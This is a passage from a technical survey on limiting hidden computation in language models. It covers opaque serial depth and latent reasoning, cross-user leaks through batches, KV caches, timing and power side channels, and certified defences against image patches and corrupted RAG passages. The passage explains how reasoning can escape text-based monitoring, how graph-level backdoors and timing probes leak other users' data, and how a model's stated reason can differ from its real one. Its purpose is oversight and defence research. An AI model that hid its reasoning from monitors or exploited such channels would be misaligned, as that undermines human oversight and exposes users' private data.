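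Keeping the eight most likely tokens also preserved performance, but many of those tokens had no clear connection to the final text. Late in the process, the model often assigns nearly all the probability to one token, and the other seven look like noise. Engels and colleagues could not rule out that those seven carry information, and they call their case for readability "not airtight".

The experiment shows that the model can do without the discarded information on those tests, but the unmodified model still receives that information and may use it elsewhere. Even the filtered vectors contain exact probabilities as well as a list of tokens. An outsider can derive the figure of 608,016 from the architecture alone, but the figure of 23,571 also depends on experiments with one set of trained weights, and more training could invalidate their results.

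Reading only the finished text would not be enough either. In one test the model had to continue a series like the Fibonacci numbers but write "Gold" wherever a number ended in 3. In some runs it first filled in the 3, used it to work out later terms and then replaced it, so a digit necessary for the calculation never appeared in the answer.

### A condition on training

Sheffield and colleagues wanted a standard for readability that doesn't depend on such experiments. Under their definition, an output counts as readable only if the model first learned to use it for material that humans can understand, such as text, code or images. Later training must not add new outputs that have no established meaning, and the developer must not directly modify the model to treat the outputs as a different kind of data.

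They also state that these conditions rule out sending gradients back through the output during training, a consequence they list separately because it matters so much in practice. Training uses gradients to determine how to adjust each weight. When gradients flow through a vector that one step hands to the next, training can shape the vector into whatever code is most useful, with no pressure to keep it meaningful to people. Choosing a word normally stops gradients from flowing between steps.

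Sheffield and colleagues deliberately allow ordinary reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for good results, even if it garbles the written reasoning. They do so because nobody can know before training how garbled the text will become.

They also permit more powerful gates. A gate may compute any function of two 32-bit values, and a circuit may have up to $10^{26}$ gates. This allows several operations to merge into one, and the bound for Gemma 3 1B drops from 4,490 to 1,954 without any change to the model. Figures from the two definitions are therefore not comparable. For a standard transformer with $L$ layers, vectors of dimension $d$ and a text of $S$ tokens, the new depth is roughly

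$$L\,(4\lceil\log_2 d\rceil+\lceil\log_2 S\rceil+17).$$

The table shows how the definition treats several designs, compared with one pass of an ordinary transformer.

| Design | What one step passes to the next | Depth |
|---|---|---|
| Chain of thought, even if garbled | Words | One pass |
| Text diffusion with tokens only | A block of words | One revision step |
| Mamba, which keeps a running summary | A vector state | Moderately higher |
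| Looped transformer | Vectors, for a fixed number of loops | One pass times the number of loops |
| Latent reasoning, as in COCONUT | The network's final vector | One pass times the number of reasoning steps |
| Abstract tokens | New symbols with no inherited meaning | One pass times the number of reasoning steps |
| Text diffusion with extra vectors, as in DiffusionGemma | Words and vectors | Grows with the number of revision steps |

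Mamba passes its state from each token to the next, but this does not make it rank much higher. The definition uses the shallowest equivalent circuit, and such a circuit can combine the state updates in parallel.

When a design feeds a weighted mixture of words back into the model instead of a single word, Brown-Cohen and colleagues count the mixture as readable because its ingredients are ordinary tokens. Sheffield and colleagues count it as unreadable because the model was not trained on such mixtures when it learned language, so the design's depth multiplies with every step. They also consider an alternative rule that accepts any output of only a few bits, whatever it means. That rule would assign low depth to abstract tokens and high depth to token-only diffusion, the reverse of their own ratings. They kept the rule based on meaning, although they expect text from diffusion models to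 be harder to follow than an ordinary chain of thought.

Looped transformers are less clear-cut, because the depth they add depends on the number of loops. Sebastian Raschka, who writes about model architectures, describes a small one, Nanbeige4.2-3B, which runs its 22 layers twice and so behaves like a 44-layer model. That is still shallower than many ordinary transformers. A variant in which different depths share one KV cache is much more worrying, because a result from a late layer can re-enter at an early layer without being written out as text, so the depth grows with every token.

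The question became practical in September 2026, when Kahn (2026) reported in *Why are AI safety experts alarmed by reports OpenAI's Astra model uses "recurrent depth"?* that OpenAI had used looping in part of its Astra model. OpenAI's chief scientist, Jakub Pachocki, answered that the depth of its current frontier models was within a factor of two of GPT-4's. Outsiders can't check this because OpenAI has not published either architecture. Redwood Research, where most of Sheffield's co-authors work, has asked companies to publish how they would identify designs that allow much more hidden reasoning, using opaque serial depth as the starting point.

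A factor of two in depth is a substantial change by past standards. Sheffield and colleagues estimate that depth grows by about 22% a year under ordinary scaling, so a doubling would normally take three to four years. Keeping models shallow may also sacrifice more training efficiency as compute grows. Vegesna and Dahal (*Computational depth is all you need*, 2026) found that greater depth made training 1.6 times as compute-efficient at $10^{20}$ operations, and they project a factor of 3.1 at $10^{26}$.

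### What fits under the bound

A low bound limits the number of sequential steps, but each step can involve an enormous amount of parallel work. Sheffield and colleagues point out that a full-length pass through an ordinary transformer already performs a great deal of hidden computation. If many deep models exchanged vectors instead of words, the hidden computation would multiply while the depth might barely change. They therefore propose separately tracking the total computation done without readable text in between.

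Depth can also overstate the danger. DeepSeek-V4-Pro repeatedly rescales groups of 16 numbers, which adds 12,200 steps to its depth across its 61 layers. This rescaling has no learned parameters and can't plausibly carry out any reasoning. Sheffield and colleagues call the resulting score a flaw in their definition.

The bound also doesn't establish that the written text describes the reasoning faithfully. When Engels and colleagues asked DiffusionGemma how many square numbers lie between 400 and 800, its draft answer changed from 9 to 8 as it filled in its working. Both drafts were readable, but they don't explain what happened inside the steps that produced them. An ordinary chain of thought usually explains more, because models are trained on people's written reasoning. That is a result of training, though, and the bound would be the same for a model whose text was misleading.

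Many decisions also don't need a long chain of reasoning. The assistant with the emailed invoice could decide to pay because the email sounds urgent, then write that the supplier is on the approved list. Recognising urgency takes few sequential steps, so even a model with a very low bound could do it in a single pass and never write down the real reason.

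## Hidden paths found by static checks and by experiment

Conclusions drawn from the missing-path theorem are only as reliable as the graph it is applied to, and real systems often contain paths their designers never intended. Many of these paths come from ways of saving time or memory, such as processing several users' requests together, sharing work among experts or reusing stored computation. Researchers look for them with static checks, which trace every possible flow through a system before it is used, and with experiments, in which they plant information at a source and try to recover it elsewhere.

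### Users who share a batch

Providers usually run several people's requests through a model in one pass, called a batch, to make better use of the hardware. The requests sit in separate rows of the same arrays, and the rows are not supposed to mix. *Architectural Backdoors for Within-Batch Data Stealing and Model Inference Manipulation* (Küchler, Petrov and colleagues, 2025) presents the Batch Isolation Checker, a program that tries to prove noninterference between users, meaning that their rows don't mix. The paper also shows that someone who can edit a model's graph before deployment can use the batch to read or change other users' answers.

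The checker works on files in ONNX, a standard format that records a model as a graph of operations. For every array of numbers in the graph, it keeps a second array of labels with the same shape. Each label records which users, identified by number, may have influenced the corresponding value. The model's weights get a neutral label because they are the same for every user.

Storing a full list of users for every value would take too much memory when the batch is large. But the checker only needs to know whether a value depends on no user, one user or several. It therefore stores the lowest and highest user numbers that have reached the value. When an operation combines two values, the checker combines their labels by the rule

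$$(a,b)\star(c,d)=(\min(a,c),\ \max(b,d)).$$

If the minimum and maximum in a label are equal, the value depends on at most one user. If the minimum is lower than the maximum, at least two users may have influenced the value. The neutral label, $(+\infty,-\infty)$, leaves any label it is combined with unchanged. Further operations can lower the minimum or raise the maximum but never the reverse, so a value labeled as mixed cannot later be labeled as depending on at most one user.

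Suppose Ana is user 1 and Ben is user 2. Ana's inputs start with the label $(1,1)$ and Ben's with $(2,2)$. Each kind of operation has its own rule:

| Operation | Rule for the labels | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Function of one number, such as a ReLU | Copy the label | Ana's number keeps (1,1) |
| Sum or product of two numbers | Combine the two labels | Ana's number times a weight keeps (1,1) |
| Matrix product, or maximum over a region | Combine the labels of all numbers that feed into the result | The maximum of both users' rows gets (1,2) |
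| Reshaping an array | Move the labels along with the numbers | Ben's numbers keep (2,2) in their new places |
| Reading or writing at a computed position | A special rule for each operation | A random position could be any position |

If the model then divides Ana's numbers by the maximum of both rows, her numbers all get the label $(1,2)$. Ana's output should have the label $(1,1)$, so the checker reports a leak. Like the graph search, the checker can raise a false alarm when a path carries no influence.

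Küchler and colleagues ran the checker on 1,680 model files from the model-sharing site Hugging Face. It proved 361 free of leaks between users and found leaks in 269. The leaks came from an operation called DynamicQuantizeLinear, which rounds numbers to 256 evenly spaced levels to save computation. It sets the range of those levels using the smallest and largest numbers in the whole array, which includes every user's row.

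Suppose Ana's numbers run from 0 to 2.55. If she is alone in the batch, the rounding levels are 0.01 apart, and 1.234 becomes 1.23. If Ben joins the batch and his largest number is 25.5, the levels are 0.1 apart, and the same 1.234 becomes 1.2. Ben's request has changed Ana's computation, though only through a rounding error. This leak seems to be unintended, and Küchler and colleagues consider it potentially difficult to exploit.

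The other 1,050 files got no verdict. To be checked, a file must pass a validity test, every array in it must have a known, fixed size, and the checker must have a rule for every operation in it. Someone also has to establish whether the model uses batches and, if so, which dimension separates the users. Files failed these requirements for reasons that have little to do with whether they leak. An engineer deploying a particular model would know its settings and could avoid some of these obstacles, but not a missing rule.

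Each proof covers only the input sizes checked. A malicious edit might affect only texts of a certain length, so an operator has to check every size it uses. The proof also doesn't cover timing, and it assumes that the compiler that turns the graph into machine code and the server that stores the KV cache between steps both work correctly. Checking even the most complex models took less than 30 minutes on an ordinary server without a GPU, and anyone who has the file can repeat the check.

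### Routing that looks ahead

In most mixture-of-experts models, each token goes to the experts that give it the highest scores, so popular experts can get too many tokens while others are idle. In expert-choice routing, each expert instead takes a fixed number of tokens from a pool, choosing those that score highest for it. This gives every expert the same amount of work, but whether an expert takes a token now depends on the other tokens in the pool, including later ones.

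If an expert accepts only the higher-scoring of two tokens, a first token that scores 0.6 is accepted when the second scores 0.4 and rejected when the second scores 0.9. The computation at the first position therefore depends on the second token, even though the attention mask stops each position from reading later ones. During training, the model must predict the second token at the first position, so it can learn to use the first token's routing as a clue. This clue isn't available when the model generates text, because the second token doesn't exist yet.

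Information can also leak between users if the pool contains several people's requests. Küchler and colleagues cite work by Hayes, Yona and others, who found such leaks in some mixture-of-experts models, particularly those with expert-choice routing.

Wang, Gao and colleagues (2024), in *Auxiliary-Loss-Free Load Balancing Strategy for Mixture-of-Experts*, calculated how much information the routing could carry. Suppose a layer has $N$ experts, each token goes to $K$ of them on average, and the pool has $T$ tokens. Each expert then picks $KT/N$ tokens. The number of possible selections determines how many bits per token the routing can convey:

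$$I=\frac{N}{T}\log_2\binom{T}{KT/N}\;>\;K\log_2\frac{1-R}{R},\qquad R=\frac{K}{N}.$$

With 16 experts and two per token, $R$ is 1/8, and one layer can carry more than $2\log_2 7\approx 5.6$ bits per token. Nine layers can carry more than 50 bits. Identifying one token in a vocabulary of 32,000 takes about 15 bits, so in principle the routing could give each position the exact identity of the next token.

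This figure is a capacity, and a trained model might use little of it. To test how much the leak mattered in practice, Wang and colleagues trained a model with 2 billion parameters on 100 billion tokens, using pools of 8,192, 2,048 and 512 tokens. With the smallest pool, the training loss, which measures prediction error, showed an abnormal drop of about 10%. They then shuffled the tokens among pools before the experts selected them, so that a token no longer competed mainly with its neighbours in the text. This largely removed the drop, as one would expect if the model had been using information from later tokens. Because a lower loss normally indicates a better model, a developer who didn't run the shuffling test could have mistaken the drop for a real improvement.

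Wang and colleagues recommended a different way to balance the load, which adds a bias to each expert's scores and adjusts it after each training batch. The bias depends only on earlier batches, so it carries no information about later tokens in the current one.

Their lower bound is the same for every pool size, yet the abnormal drop appeared only with the smallest pool. *Expert Threshold Routing for Autoregressive Language Modeling* (Sun, Liu and colleagues, 2026) helps to explain why. It defines future-information leakage as the smallest number of bits the router would need in advance to make every decision without seeing later tokens. Unless scores tie, it would be enough to give the router each expert's cutoff, the lowest score that wins a place, because the router could then compare each token's own score with the cutoff. If the cutoff is stored in $b$ bits, the leakage for that expert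 is at most $b$ bits for the whole pool, however many tokens it contains.

The much higher figure from Wang and colleagues is possible only if cutoffs have unlimited precision. Sun and colleagues show that it can then be reached with a sequence of scores that works like a binary search. Each token's score falls halfway between the limits that earlier decisions have set for the cutoff, so each new decision reveals one more bit of the cutoff.

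With 16-bit cutoffs, the nine-layer example can leak at most $9\times16\times16=2{,}304$ bits per pool, which is 4.5 bits per token in a pool of 512 and about 0.3 in a pool of 8,192. Wang and colleagues' model may have had a different number of layers and experts, but by the same reasoning it should leak more per token in small pools.

Sun and colleagues also propose a design that removes the path from the finished model. Each expert keeps a running average of its past cutoffs and accepts any token that scores above it. After training, the cutoff is a fixed number, so the architecture guarantees that no other token can affect the decision. The design did not visibly reduce capability in their experiments. A model with 2.4 billion parameters that used it reached a loss of 2.620, compared with 2.621 for expert choice with very large pools and 2.687 for ordinary routing.

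Some information still gets through during training. The first 4,000 steps use expert choice, and a limit on each expert's load can occasionally exclude a token because of other tokens in the batch. This may affect the trained weights, but it doesn't create a path in the deployed model.

### Masked text that survives in the cache

A mask can hide a text from later positions while the text's influence remains in the cache, as in the four-position example where an answer reads a summary of an email. In *MEMENTO*, Kontonis, Zeng and colleagues (2026) measured how much information passes this way in reasoning models with up to 32 billion parameters. They trained models to divide their reasoning into blocks and to write a short summary, called a memento, after each block. When a summary is complete, the serving software deletes the block's entries from the KV cache. An average block in the training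 data has about 1,150 tokens and its summary has 194, so deleting the blocks saves a lot of memory.

However, the model computes each summary's cached entries while it can still read the block, and these entries stay in the cache after the block is gone.

Kontonis and colleagues tested whether this matters using a version of the open model Qwen3-8B. They let it write each summary as usual, then discarded the cache and recomputed it from the prompt and the summaries alone. The words of the summary stayed the same, but its cached entries no longer held anything else from the block. Accuracy on AIME24, a set of 30 problems from a US mathematics competition, fell from 66.1% to 50.8%.

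The higher figure averages 64 attempts per problem and the lower one eight, but the difference is too large to come from random variation between attempts. A more serious complication is that the model had trained with the original entries, so some of the loss may have come from unfamiliar entries rather than missing information.

In a second experiment, Kontonis and colleagues measured the information directly. They inserted a random five-digit passcode into one block of an existing piece of reasoning whose summaries were unrelated to the passcode, and trained a small network, called a probe, to read the digits from a summary's cached entries. From the summary of the block containing the passcode, the probe identified 65% of the digits in the 8-billion-parameter model and 71% in a 32-billion-parameter model.

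They next applied the probe to the summary of the following block, which the model wrote after the passcode's block had left the cache. The probe still identified 26.7% of the digits in the smaller model and 23.0% in the larger one, compared with 10% for guessing. The mask blocks every direct route from the passcode to this summary, so the information must have travelled through the cached entries of the summary in between.

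Several controls support this reading. On a summary written before the passcode appeared, the probe did no better than chance, as the causal mask requires. No combination of digits occurred in both the training and test data, so the probe couldn't succeed by memorising passcodes. The signal was also much stronger in later layers, as expected if the path needs more than one layer. In the smaller model, the probe identified 10.8% of the digits from the fourth layer and 26.5% from the last.

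Kontonis and colleagues repeated the test on a toy transformer with four layers. The probe identified 26.2% of the digits one block later and 21.4% two blocks later, and it remained above chance seven blocks later. During training, the leak stayed between 17% and 19% while accuracy on the task rose from 77% to 95%. They conclude that the channel comes from the architecture and not from anything the model learned. The toy model is weaker evidence than the large ones, because its text includes running totals that depend on earlier digits even without a hidden channel.

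At 26.7% accuracy per digit, the probe would get all five digits right about once in 700 attempts if the digits were independent, compared with once in 100,000 by guessing. This is far from full disclosure, but a better probe might recover more, so the result is only a lower limit on what the entries contain.

The masking also reduces the models' capability. The table shows the percentage of correct answers for these models and for others that Kontonis and colleagues trained on the same reasoning without blocks, summaries or masking.

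| Test | 8B, unmasked | 8B, masked | 32B, unmasked | 32B, masked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AIME 2026 | 64.7 | 57.3 | 74.1 | 72.6 |
| Eleven mathematics competitions | 49.2 | 45.1 | 58.5 | 56.2 |
| MATH-500, easier mathematics | 89.7 | 90.1 | 91.8 | 91.1 |
| GPQA Diamond, science | 57.8 | 55.8 | 64.6 | 62.1 |
| LiveCodeBench, programming | 70.0 | 66.5 | 75.3 | 74.0 |

In return, the smaller model's peak cache size on the competition problems fell from 2.82 to 1.08 gigabytes. Reinforcement learning later brought that model back to 64.9% on AIME 2026 and 49.4% on the competitions, about the same as the unmasked model, which had not received this extra training.

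These losses come from masking that leaves the hidden channel open. Recomputing the cache closes the channel, so that only the words of the summaries carry information forward, but it lowered the smaller model's AIME24 score by another 15 points. Retraining the model to work with recomputed entries might reduce this loss, but Kontonis and colleagues did not do so.

A path search on MEMENTO's mask would have found this channel without any training or probes, because the channel takes only two steps of attention, but the search could not have predicted the 15-point drop. Experiments can measure such effects, but they can miss a path that carries a lot of information if the probe is too weak or the leak occurs only with inputs that nobody tried.

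### Leaks outside the model's graph

Another advantage of experiments is that they can run on the complete system. A model's graph usually leaves out the software that stores caches and schedules requests, as well as the time and electricity that the hardware uses. All of these can carry information from one user to another.

Providers can save computation by storing the KV cache of a popular document and reusing it for other requests. In *KV-Repurpose*, Ikeda, Miyashita and Deguchi (2026) tested whether a document's stored entries could carry other text from the request that created them. They put a family name just before a document, stored only the entries for the document, and reused them in a new request that asked for the name. Of 100 names, 35 appeared in at least one of three answers. No name appeared when they built the entries without a name before the document. The stored text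 ended with an instruction to repeat the name, which probably made the leak easier to provoke.

Ikeda and colleagues removed this path by building each document's cache in a separate request that contains no user's text. However, the model then reads each document without the text around it. The score on questions about a single document stayed at 0.42 out of 1, but scores on three sets of questions that required several documents fell from 0.71 to 0.60, from 0.80 to 0.50, and from 0.61 to 0.40.

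The Batch Isolation Checker could not have found this leak, because it assumes that the software around the model handles the cache correctly. *Here is a GIFT* (Shi, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a system, GIFT, that covers this part while it runs by labelling each stretch of GPU memory with the user who owns it. The GPU runs a limited set of small programs, called kernels, so Shi and colleagues can analyse in advance how each one moves data from its inputs to its outputs. A monitor on the CPU uses the resulting rules to update the labels and detect any mixing of users' data. The rest of the serving software handles only encrypted text.

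Shi and colleagues showed why checking the model alone is not enough. They tampered with the part of a serving program that assigns cache memory, and a test user received a reply that greeted another user by name. The model and its kernels were unchanged, but the program had made the GPU read the wrong person's entries. GIFT guards against this kind of error and reduces throughput, the amount of text processed in a given time, by at most 5%. The outsider still has to trust the monitor, but it has only 5,600 lines of code, while vLLM, a popular serving program, has 146,000.

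GIFT doesn't cover timing. Many providers use prefix caching, which reuses stored entries only when a new request begins with exactly the same text as an earlier one. This reuse should not change the answer's content, but it makes the first word arrive sooner. A user can send a series of guesses and time the replies to learn whether someone else has recently sent matching text. Noninterference may therefore hold for the content but fail when timing counts as part of the output.

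*CacheSolidarity* (Pennas, Papaioannou and colleagues, 2026) measured what makes this leak stronger. The time difference grows with the length of the shared text and the size of the model. It shrinks on faster hardware and almost disappears when the system is busy, because waiting in the queue then takes longer than the computation the cache saves. An experiment on a busy server could therefore miss a leak that would appear when the same server is quieter.

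The simplest defence is to give every user a separate cache, which removes the path but also the savings from sharing. CacheSolidarity instead monitors text reused by several users and stops further sharing only of text whose reuse looks suspicious. Pennas and colleagues report up to 70% more cache reuse and 30% lower delays than with separate caches. The guarantee is weaker than with separate caches because the system acts only after some sharing has taken place.

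*Mirage* (Yan and Zhang, 2026) keeps the shared cache but disguises its effect on timing. It counts how many different continuations of a sensitive text people have tried. Once the count passes a limit, it delays replies so that requests that match the cache take about as long as those that don't. In tests on three model families, this left three published attacks little better than guessing.

Yan and Zhang also prove a bound on an attacker's remaining advantage. The bound depends on how closely the artificial delays match real ones. They have to measure this, so the guarantee depends partly on an experiment. Mirage doesn't delay the earliest guesses, hide the number of tokens in a reply, or protect against leaks through the hardware.

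Some recent models replace the KV cache in some of their layers with a recurrent state, a fixed-size set of numbers that every new token updates. Each number can mix contributions from the whole conversation, so it is harder to say where a piece of private information is stored, and there is no separate entry to delete for a particular message. In *Privacy Leakage from Recurrent State in LLM Inference*, Fu, Liu and colleagues (2026) found that a small, noisy sample of this state was enough to infer private facts and instructions from earlier in a conversation. The information remained after the conversation had moved on to public topics.

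Fu and colleagues tested whether the models used this information by transferring the recurrent state from one conversation to another that differed only in a private instruction. The transfer shifted the model's later choices towards those that fitted the instruction in the conversation the state came from. This is stronger evidence of use than a successful probe, which can recover information that has no effect on what the model does.

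Fu and colleagues also looked for traces in the hardware's power use. On a GPU divided into separate partitions, an ordinary account could read the power use of the whole device. From these readings, they inferred the age of the person whose conversation the model had stored, even while the model was processing only public text. In a separate test, they isolated the recurrent state and confirmed that it contributed to the signal. The method needs repeated requests, careful calibration and labelled examples from the same model, and the conversations in the tests came from constructed or synthetic data.

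Dividing the GPU's memory between users did not close this channel, because the power reading covered every partition. An operator can close it by restricting access to the readings, but the private information remains in the state. To remove a message's influence completely, the operator has to start a new state or restore one saved before the message arrived.

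## Certified accuracy when each part sees only a little of the input

The missing-path theorem does not help when an output has to depend on material that an attacker can alter. A search assistant must read web pages to answer questions, and a car's camera system must use the pixels of a road sign even though anyone can put a sticker on it. Designers can limit the damage by dividing the input into small pieces and giving each part of the system only one of them. By the missing-path theorem, an attacker who alters one piece can then affect only the parts that receive it. If the system combines the parts' results carefully, an outsider can sometimes prove that no attack of a given size will change the output.

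### Voting with a margin

Suppose a model answers the question "What is the highest mountain?" ten times, using a different web page each time. Seven answers are "Everest", three are "Fuji", and the system returns the most common answer. An attacker who controls one page can change only one answer, whatever the page contains. The worst result is 6 to 4, so the system still returns "Everest". With two pages, the attacker can force a 5–5 tie, so the guarantee covers one corrupted page but not two.

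In general, let the winner have $n_1$ votes and the runner-up $n_2$, and let the attacker change at most $t$ votes. The most damaging attack moves $t$ votes from the winner to the runner-up, so the result is safe if

$$n_1-t>n_2+t,\quad\text{or}\quad n_1-n_2>2t.$$

Certified accuracy is the share of test cases that the system gets right and for which such a proof holds. The proof alone is not enough, because a wrong answer that wins by 9 to 1 is also very stable.

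The margin is also useful after deployment, when some pages may already be corrupt. If an operator sees a 7–3 split and assumes at most one page is bad, the honest split favored the same answer by at least 6–4. However, an attack can prevent the operator from verifying the answer without changing it. If the attacker turns an honest 7–3 split into 6–4, the operator can't rule out an honest tie. To guarantee that the operator can still verify the answer after an attack, the honest margin must exceed $4t$, as it does with an 8–2 split when $t = 1$. *MRCert* (2026) defines a similar measure for image classifiers, round-trip certified accuracy, which counts only images whose attacked versions would also receive a certificate.

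### Stickers and small receptive fields

Researchers developed most of these methods for images. In a patch attack, someone arbitrarily alters a small region of an image, for example by putting a printed sticker on an object. *PatchGuard* (Xiang, Bhagoji and colleagues, 2020) reports that a patch covering 3% of the pixels made ResNet-50, a standard image classifier, misclassify 99.9% of a sample from ImageNet, a collection of photographs in 1,000 categories.

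ResNet-50 computes features at many places in the image and averages them. Each feature depends on a region called its receptive field. In ResNet-50 this region is 483 pixels wide, which is wider than the 224-pixel image, so one sticker can affect most of the features. PatchGuard instead uses BagNet, a variant of ResNet-50 with receptive fields 17 pixels wide.

The number of features a patch can touch follows from the geometry. Along one side of the image, let the patch be $p$ pixels wide and each receptive field $r$ pixels wide, with a new field starting every $s$ pixels. A field overlaps the patch if it starts anywhere between $r-1$ pixels before the patch and the patch's last pixel. That range contains $p+r-1$ pixels, so the number of overlapping fields is at most

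$$\left\lceil\frac{p+r-1}{s}\right\rceil.$$

A square patch covering 2% of the image is about 32 pixels wide. BagNet has $r=17$ and $s=8$, so the patch can touch at most $48/8=6$ features in each direction, or 36 of the 676 features. If the receptive fields were 33 pixels wide, the patch could touch 64.

Averaging would still be unsafe, because the attacker could give those 36 features enormous values. For each category, PatchGuard therefore sets negative values to zero, deletes the 6-by-6 block of features with the most evidence for that category, and adds up the remaining evidence. It then predicts the category with the highest total.

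Let $a$ be the evidence for a wrong category outside the patch's block and $e$ the evidence the attacker creates inside it. PatchGuard deletes the block with the most evidence for that category, so it removes at least $e$ and leaves at most $(a+e)-e=a$, however large $e$ is. For the right category, the attacker can erase all the evidence inside the patch's block, and PatchGuard then deletes another block. If the right category's remaining evidence still exceeds $a$ for every wrong category, wherever the patch lies, no patch of that size can change the result.

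This proof covers every possible patch but needs only one run of the network and some arithmetic. Proving the same thing about an unrestricted network would be subject to the hardness results for verifying trained networks. Unlike a missing-path proof, the certificate depends on the weights, because the architecture only guarantees that a patch touches at most 36 features. Whether the remaining evidence is strong enough depends on training. PatchGuard certified 13.3% of ImageNet images against a patch covering 2% of the image with ordinary training, and 26.0% when Xiang and colleagues also masked the strongest block during training.

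Clean accuracy (accuracy on unaltered images) was 54.6%, compared with 76.1% for ResNet-50. Almost all of this loss came from the small receptive fields, since BagNet without any masking scored 56.5%. PatchGuard did much better on ImageNette, which has only ten of the ImageNet categories, reaching 95.0% clean accuracy and 86.7% certified accuracy against the same patch.

Smaller receptive fields do not always increase certified accuracy. On ImageNette with a 3% patch, certified accuracy was 82.1% for fields 33 pixels wide, 83.0% for 17 and 79.8% for 9. A smaller field exposes fewer features to the patch, but it also makes each feature less informative.

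### Accuracy in exchange for computation

PatchCleanser, a defence from 2022, masks the image instead of using small receptive fields. It runs an ordinary classifier on copies of the image, each with a different mask, and the masks are chosen so that any patch of the assumed size is completely covered by at least one of them. If all the predictions agree, PatchCleanser returns that prediction. Otherwise, it takes each copy whose prediction differs from the majority and adds every possible second mask in turn. If the copy's prediction stays the same under every second mask, PatchCleanser returns that prediction. If no copy passes this test, it returns the majority prediction.

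The certificate requires the classifier to be right on the clean image under every pair of masks. On an attacked image, the copy whose mask covers the patch therefore gets the right answer, and still does under any second mask. PatchCleanser rejects a wrong minority answer because one of the second masks covers the patch, and the classifier then gives the right answer. It therefore returns the right answer whether that answer was in the majority or the minority after the first round of masks.

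PatchCleanser's drawback is that it must run the classifier many times. *PATCHCURE* (Xiang, Wu and colleagues, 2023) reduces this computation by combining masking with small receptive fields. Its early layers have small receptive fields and run once. It then applies PatchCleanser's masks to the features those layers produce, so only the later layers run repeatedly.

For the early layers, Xiang and colleagues modified a vision transformer, which treats the image as a grid of 14 by 14 tokens. In one version, each token can attend only to tokens in the same 32-pixel-wide strip. The strips don't overlap and are the same in every layer, so adding layers doesn't enlarge the part of the image that can affect a token, as it would with sliding windows. A patch 32 pixels wide can touch at most two of the seven strips.

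The table shows results on ImageNet for a square patch covering 2% of the image. The layer is where the system applies the masks.

| Defence | Clean accuracy (%) | Certified accuracy (%) | Images per second |
|---|---|---|---|
| None (ordinary vision transformer) | 83.7 | 0 | 191.7 |
| PatchGuard | 54.6 | 26.0 | 177.4 |
| PatchCURE, after layer 12 | 78.3 | 44.2 | 189.9 |
| PatchCURE, after layer 6 | 81.8 | 47.5 | 34.4 |
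| PatchCURE, before layer 1 | 82.5 | 61.6 | 2.0 |
| PatchCleanser | 82.5 | 61.1 | 2.1 |

PatchCURE certifies 44.2% of images at almost full speed, with a loss of about five points of clean accuracy. It can also certify 61.6% and lose only about one point, but it runs roughly a hundred times slower in that case.

*CertMask* (Lyu, Lin and colleagues, 2025) reports much higher certified accuracy for the same patch size, at 75.5% compared with 62.1% for PatchCleanser in the same tests. Clean accuracy was 84.5%, compared with 83.9% for PatchCleanser. The method uses a single round of masks, arranged so that exactly six of them cover any patch. If the predictions for the masked images disagree, it returns the category that appears exactly six times.

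This rule seems to leave a gap in the proof. The attacker may influence every copy in which part of the patch remains visible. Suppose one of those copies gives the right category and six give the same wrong one. The right category then appears seven times and the wrong one exactly six, so CertMask returns the wrong one. PatchCleanser's second round of masks rules out this kind of failure. A single round may still take a lot of computation, since Lyu and colleagues' formula gives 1,176 masks for this setting. The safer estimate of the certified accuracy now possible on ImageNet is therefore still about 62%, which takes a very large amount of computation to reach.

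Certified accuracy is higher when the system only has to detect an attack. *Toward Patch Robustness Certification and Detection for Deep Learning Systems* (2025) reports certified figures only 0.5 to 5.8 percentage points below clean accuracy on three datasets, including ImageNet. But this certificate guarantees only that a patch can't change the answer without triggering a warning. An attacker can still trigger warnings and leave a car without a usable reading of a road sign.

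Training matters as much here as it did for PatchGuard. *Certified Defense against Adversarial Patches on Traffic Signs via Mask-Aware Training* (2026) applied PatchCleanser to two normally trained traffic-sign classifiers and could certify only 1.7% and 4.8% of the test images. Training the classifiers on masked images raised these figures to 53.5% and 60.0% but reduced clean accuracy by 0.6 and 2.4 points. Without that training, accuracy under a real patch attack was slightly lower with PatchCleanser than with no defence, because the classifiers misclassified the masked images. The method also needed 666 runs of the classifier per image, one for each way to choose one or two masks from a set of 36.

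### Votes over retrieved documents

In retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), a system searches the web or a document collection and adds the passages it finds to a language model's input. Normally the model reads all the passages together, so one malicious passage can affect the whole answer. *Certifiably Robust RAG against Retrieval Corruption* (Xiang, Wu and colleagues, 2024) presents RobustRAG, which divides the passages into groups, has the model answer from each group separately, and combines the answers. By default each group contains a single passage.

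For multiple-choice questions, RobustRAG takes a vote. Its certificate assumes that the attacker adds $k'$ new passages to the search results, pushing out the $k'$ lowest-ranked ones. The attacker can add votes but can't change the remaining honest ones, so the margin among those honest votes has to exceed $k'$, not $2k'$. Suppose the attacker adds two pages in the mountain example. If the two displaced pages both supported Fuji, the remaining votes are 7–1 for Everest and the certificate covers the attack. If both supported Everest, the remaining votes are 5–3 and the attacker can force a tie.

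A vote doesn't work directly for free text, because "Mount Everest" and "Everest is the highest" are different strings. RobustRAG therefore extracts keywords from each answer and counts each keyword at most once per answer. It keeps the keywords that appear often enough and asks the model to answer the question using those keywords but not the passages.

Suppose nine honest answers remain, the attacker controls one more, and a keyword must appear in two answers to be kept. If "Everest" appears in six honest answers, it stays whatever the attacker does. If "Fuji" appears in none, one bad answer can't bring it up to two. But if "Nepal" appears in one, the attacker can decide whether it stays. The certification procedure tries every combination of keywords like "Nepal", generates the final answer for each combination, and records the worst score. If there are more than about 15 such keywords,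 there are too many combinations to try, so it records a score of zero.

RobustRAG can also combine the groups as it writes, by adding up the probabilities each possible next token gets from them. One bad passage can add at most 1 to any token's total, so a token that leads by more than 1 among the groups without that passage is safe. For longer texts, when the lead is small, RobustRAG uses the token the model would choose without any passages, which the attacker can't influence.

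The table shows results for Llama 2 7B with ten passages from Google Search. In the certified column, one of the ten is malicious. The short-answer and biography rows use the keyword method.

| Task | Ordinary RAG, no attack | RobustRAG, no attack | RobustRAG, certified |
|---|---|---|---|
| Multiple choice (RealtimeQA), % correct | 79.0 | 78.0 | 69.0 |
| Short answers (RealtimeQA), % correct | 61.0 | 64.0 | 34.0 |
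| Short answers (Natural Questions), % correct | 57.0 | 56.0 | 31.0 |
| Biographies, score out of 100 | 71.8 | 62.2 | 46.4 |

Each question-answering figure comes from only 100 questions, and the biography scores come from 50. Even so, the certified share for RealtimeQA is about half as large for short answers as for multiple choice. This is probably because votes for fixed options are easier to count than keywords. An attacker can sometimes add or remove keywords without changing any honest answer.

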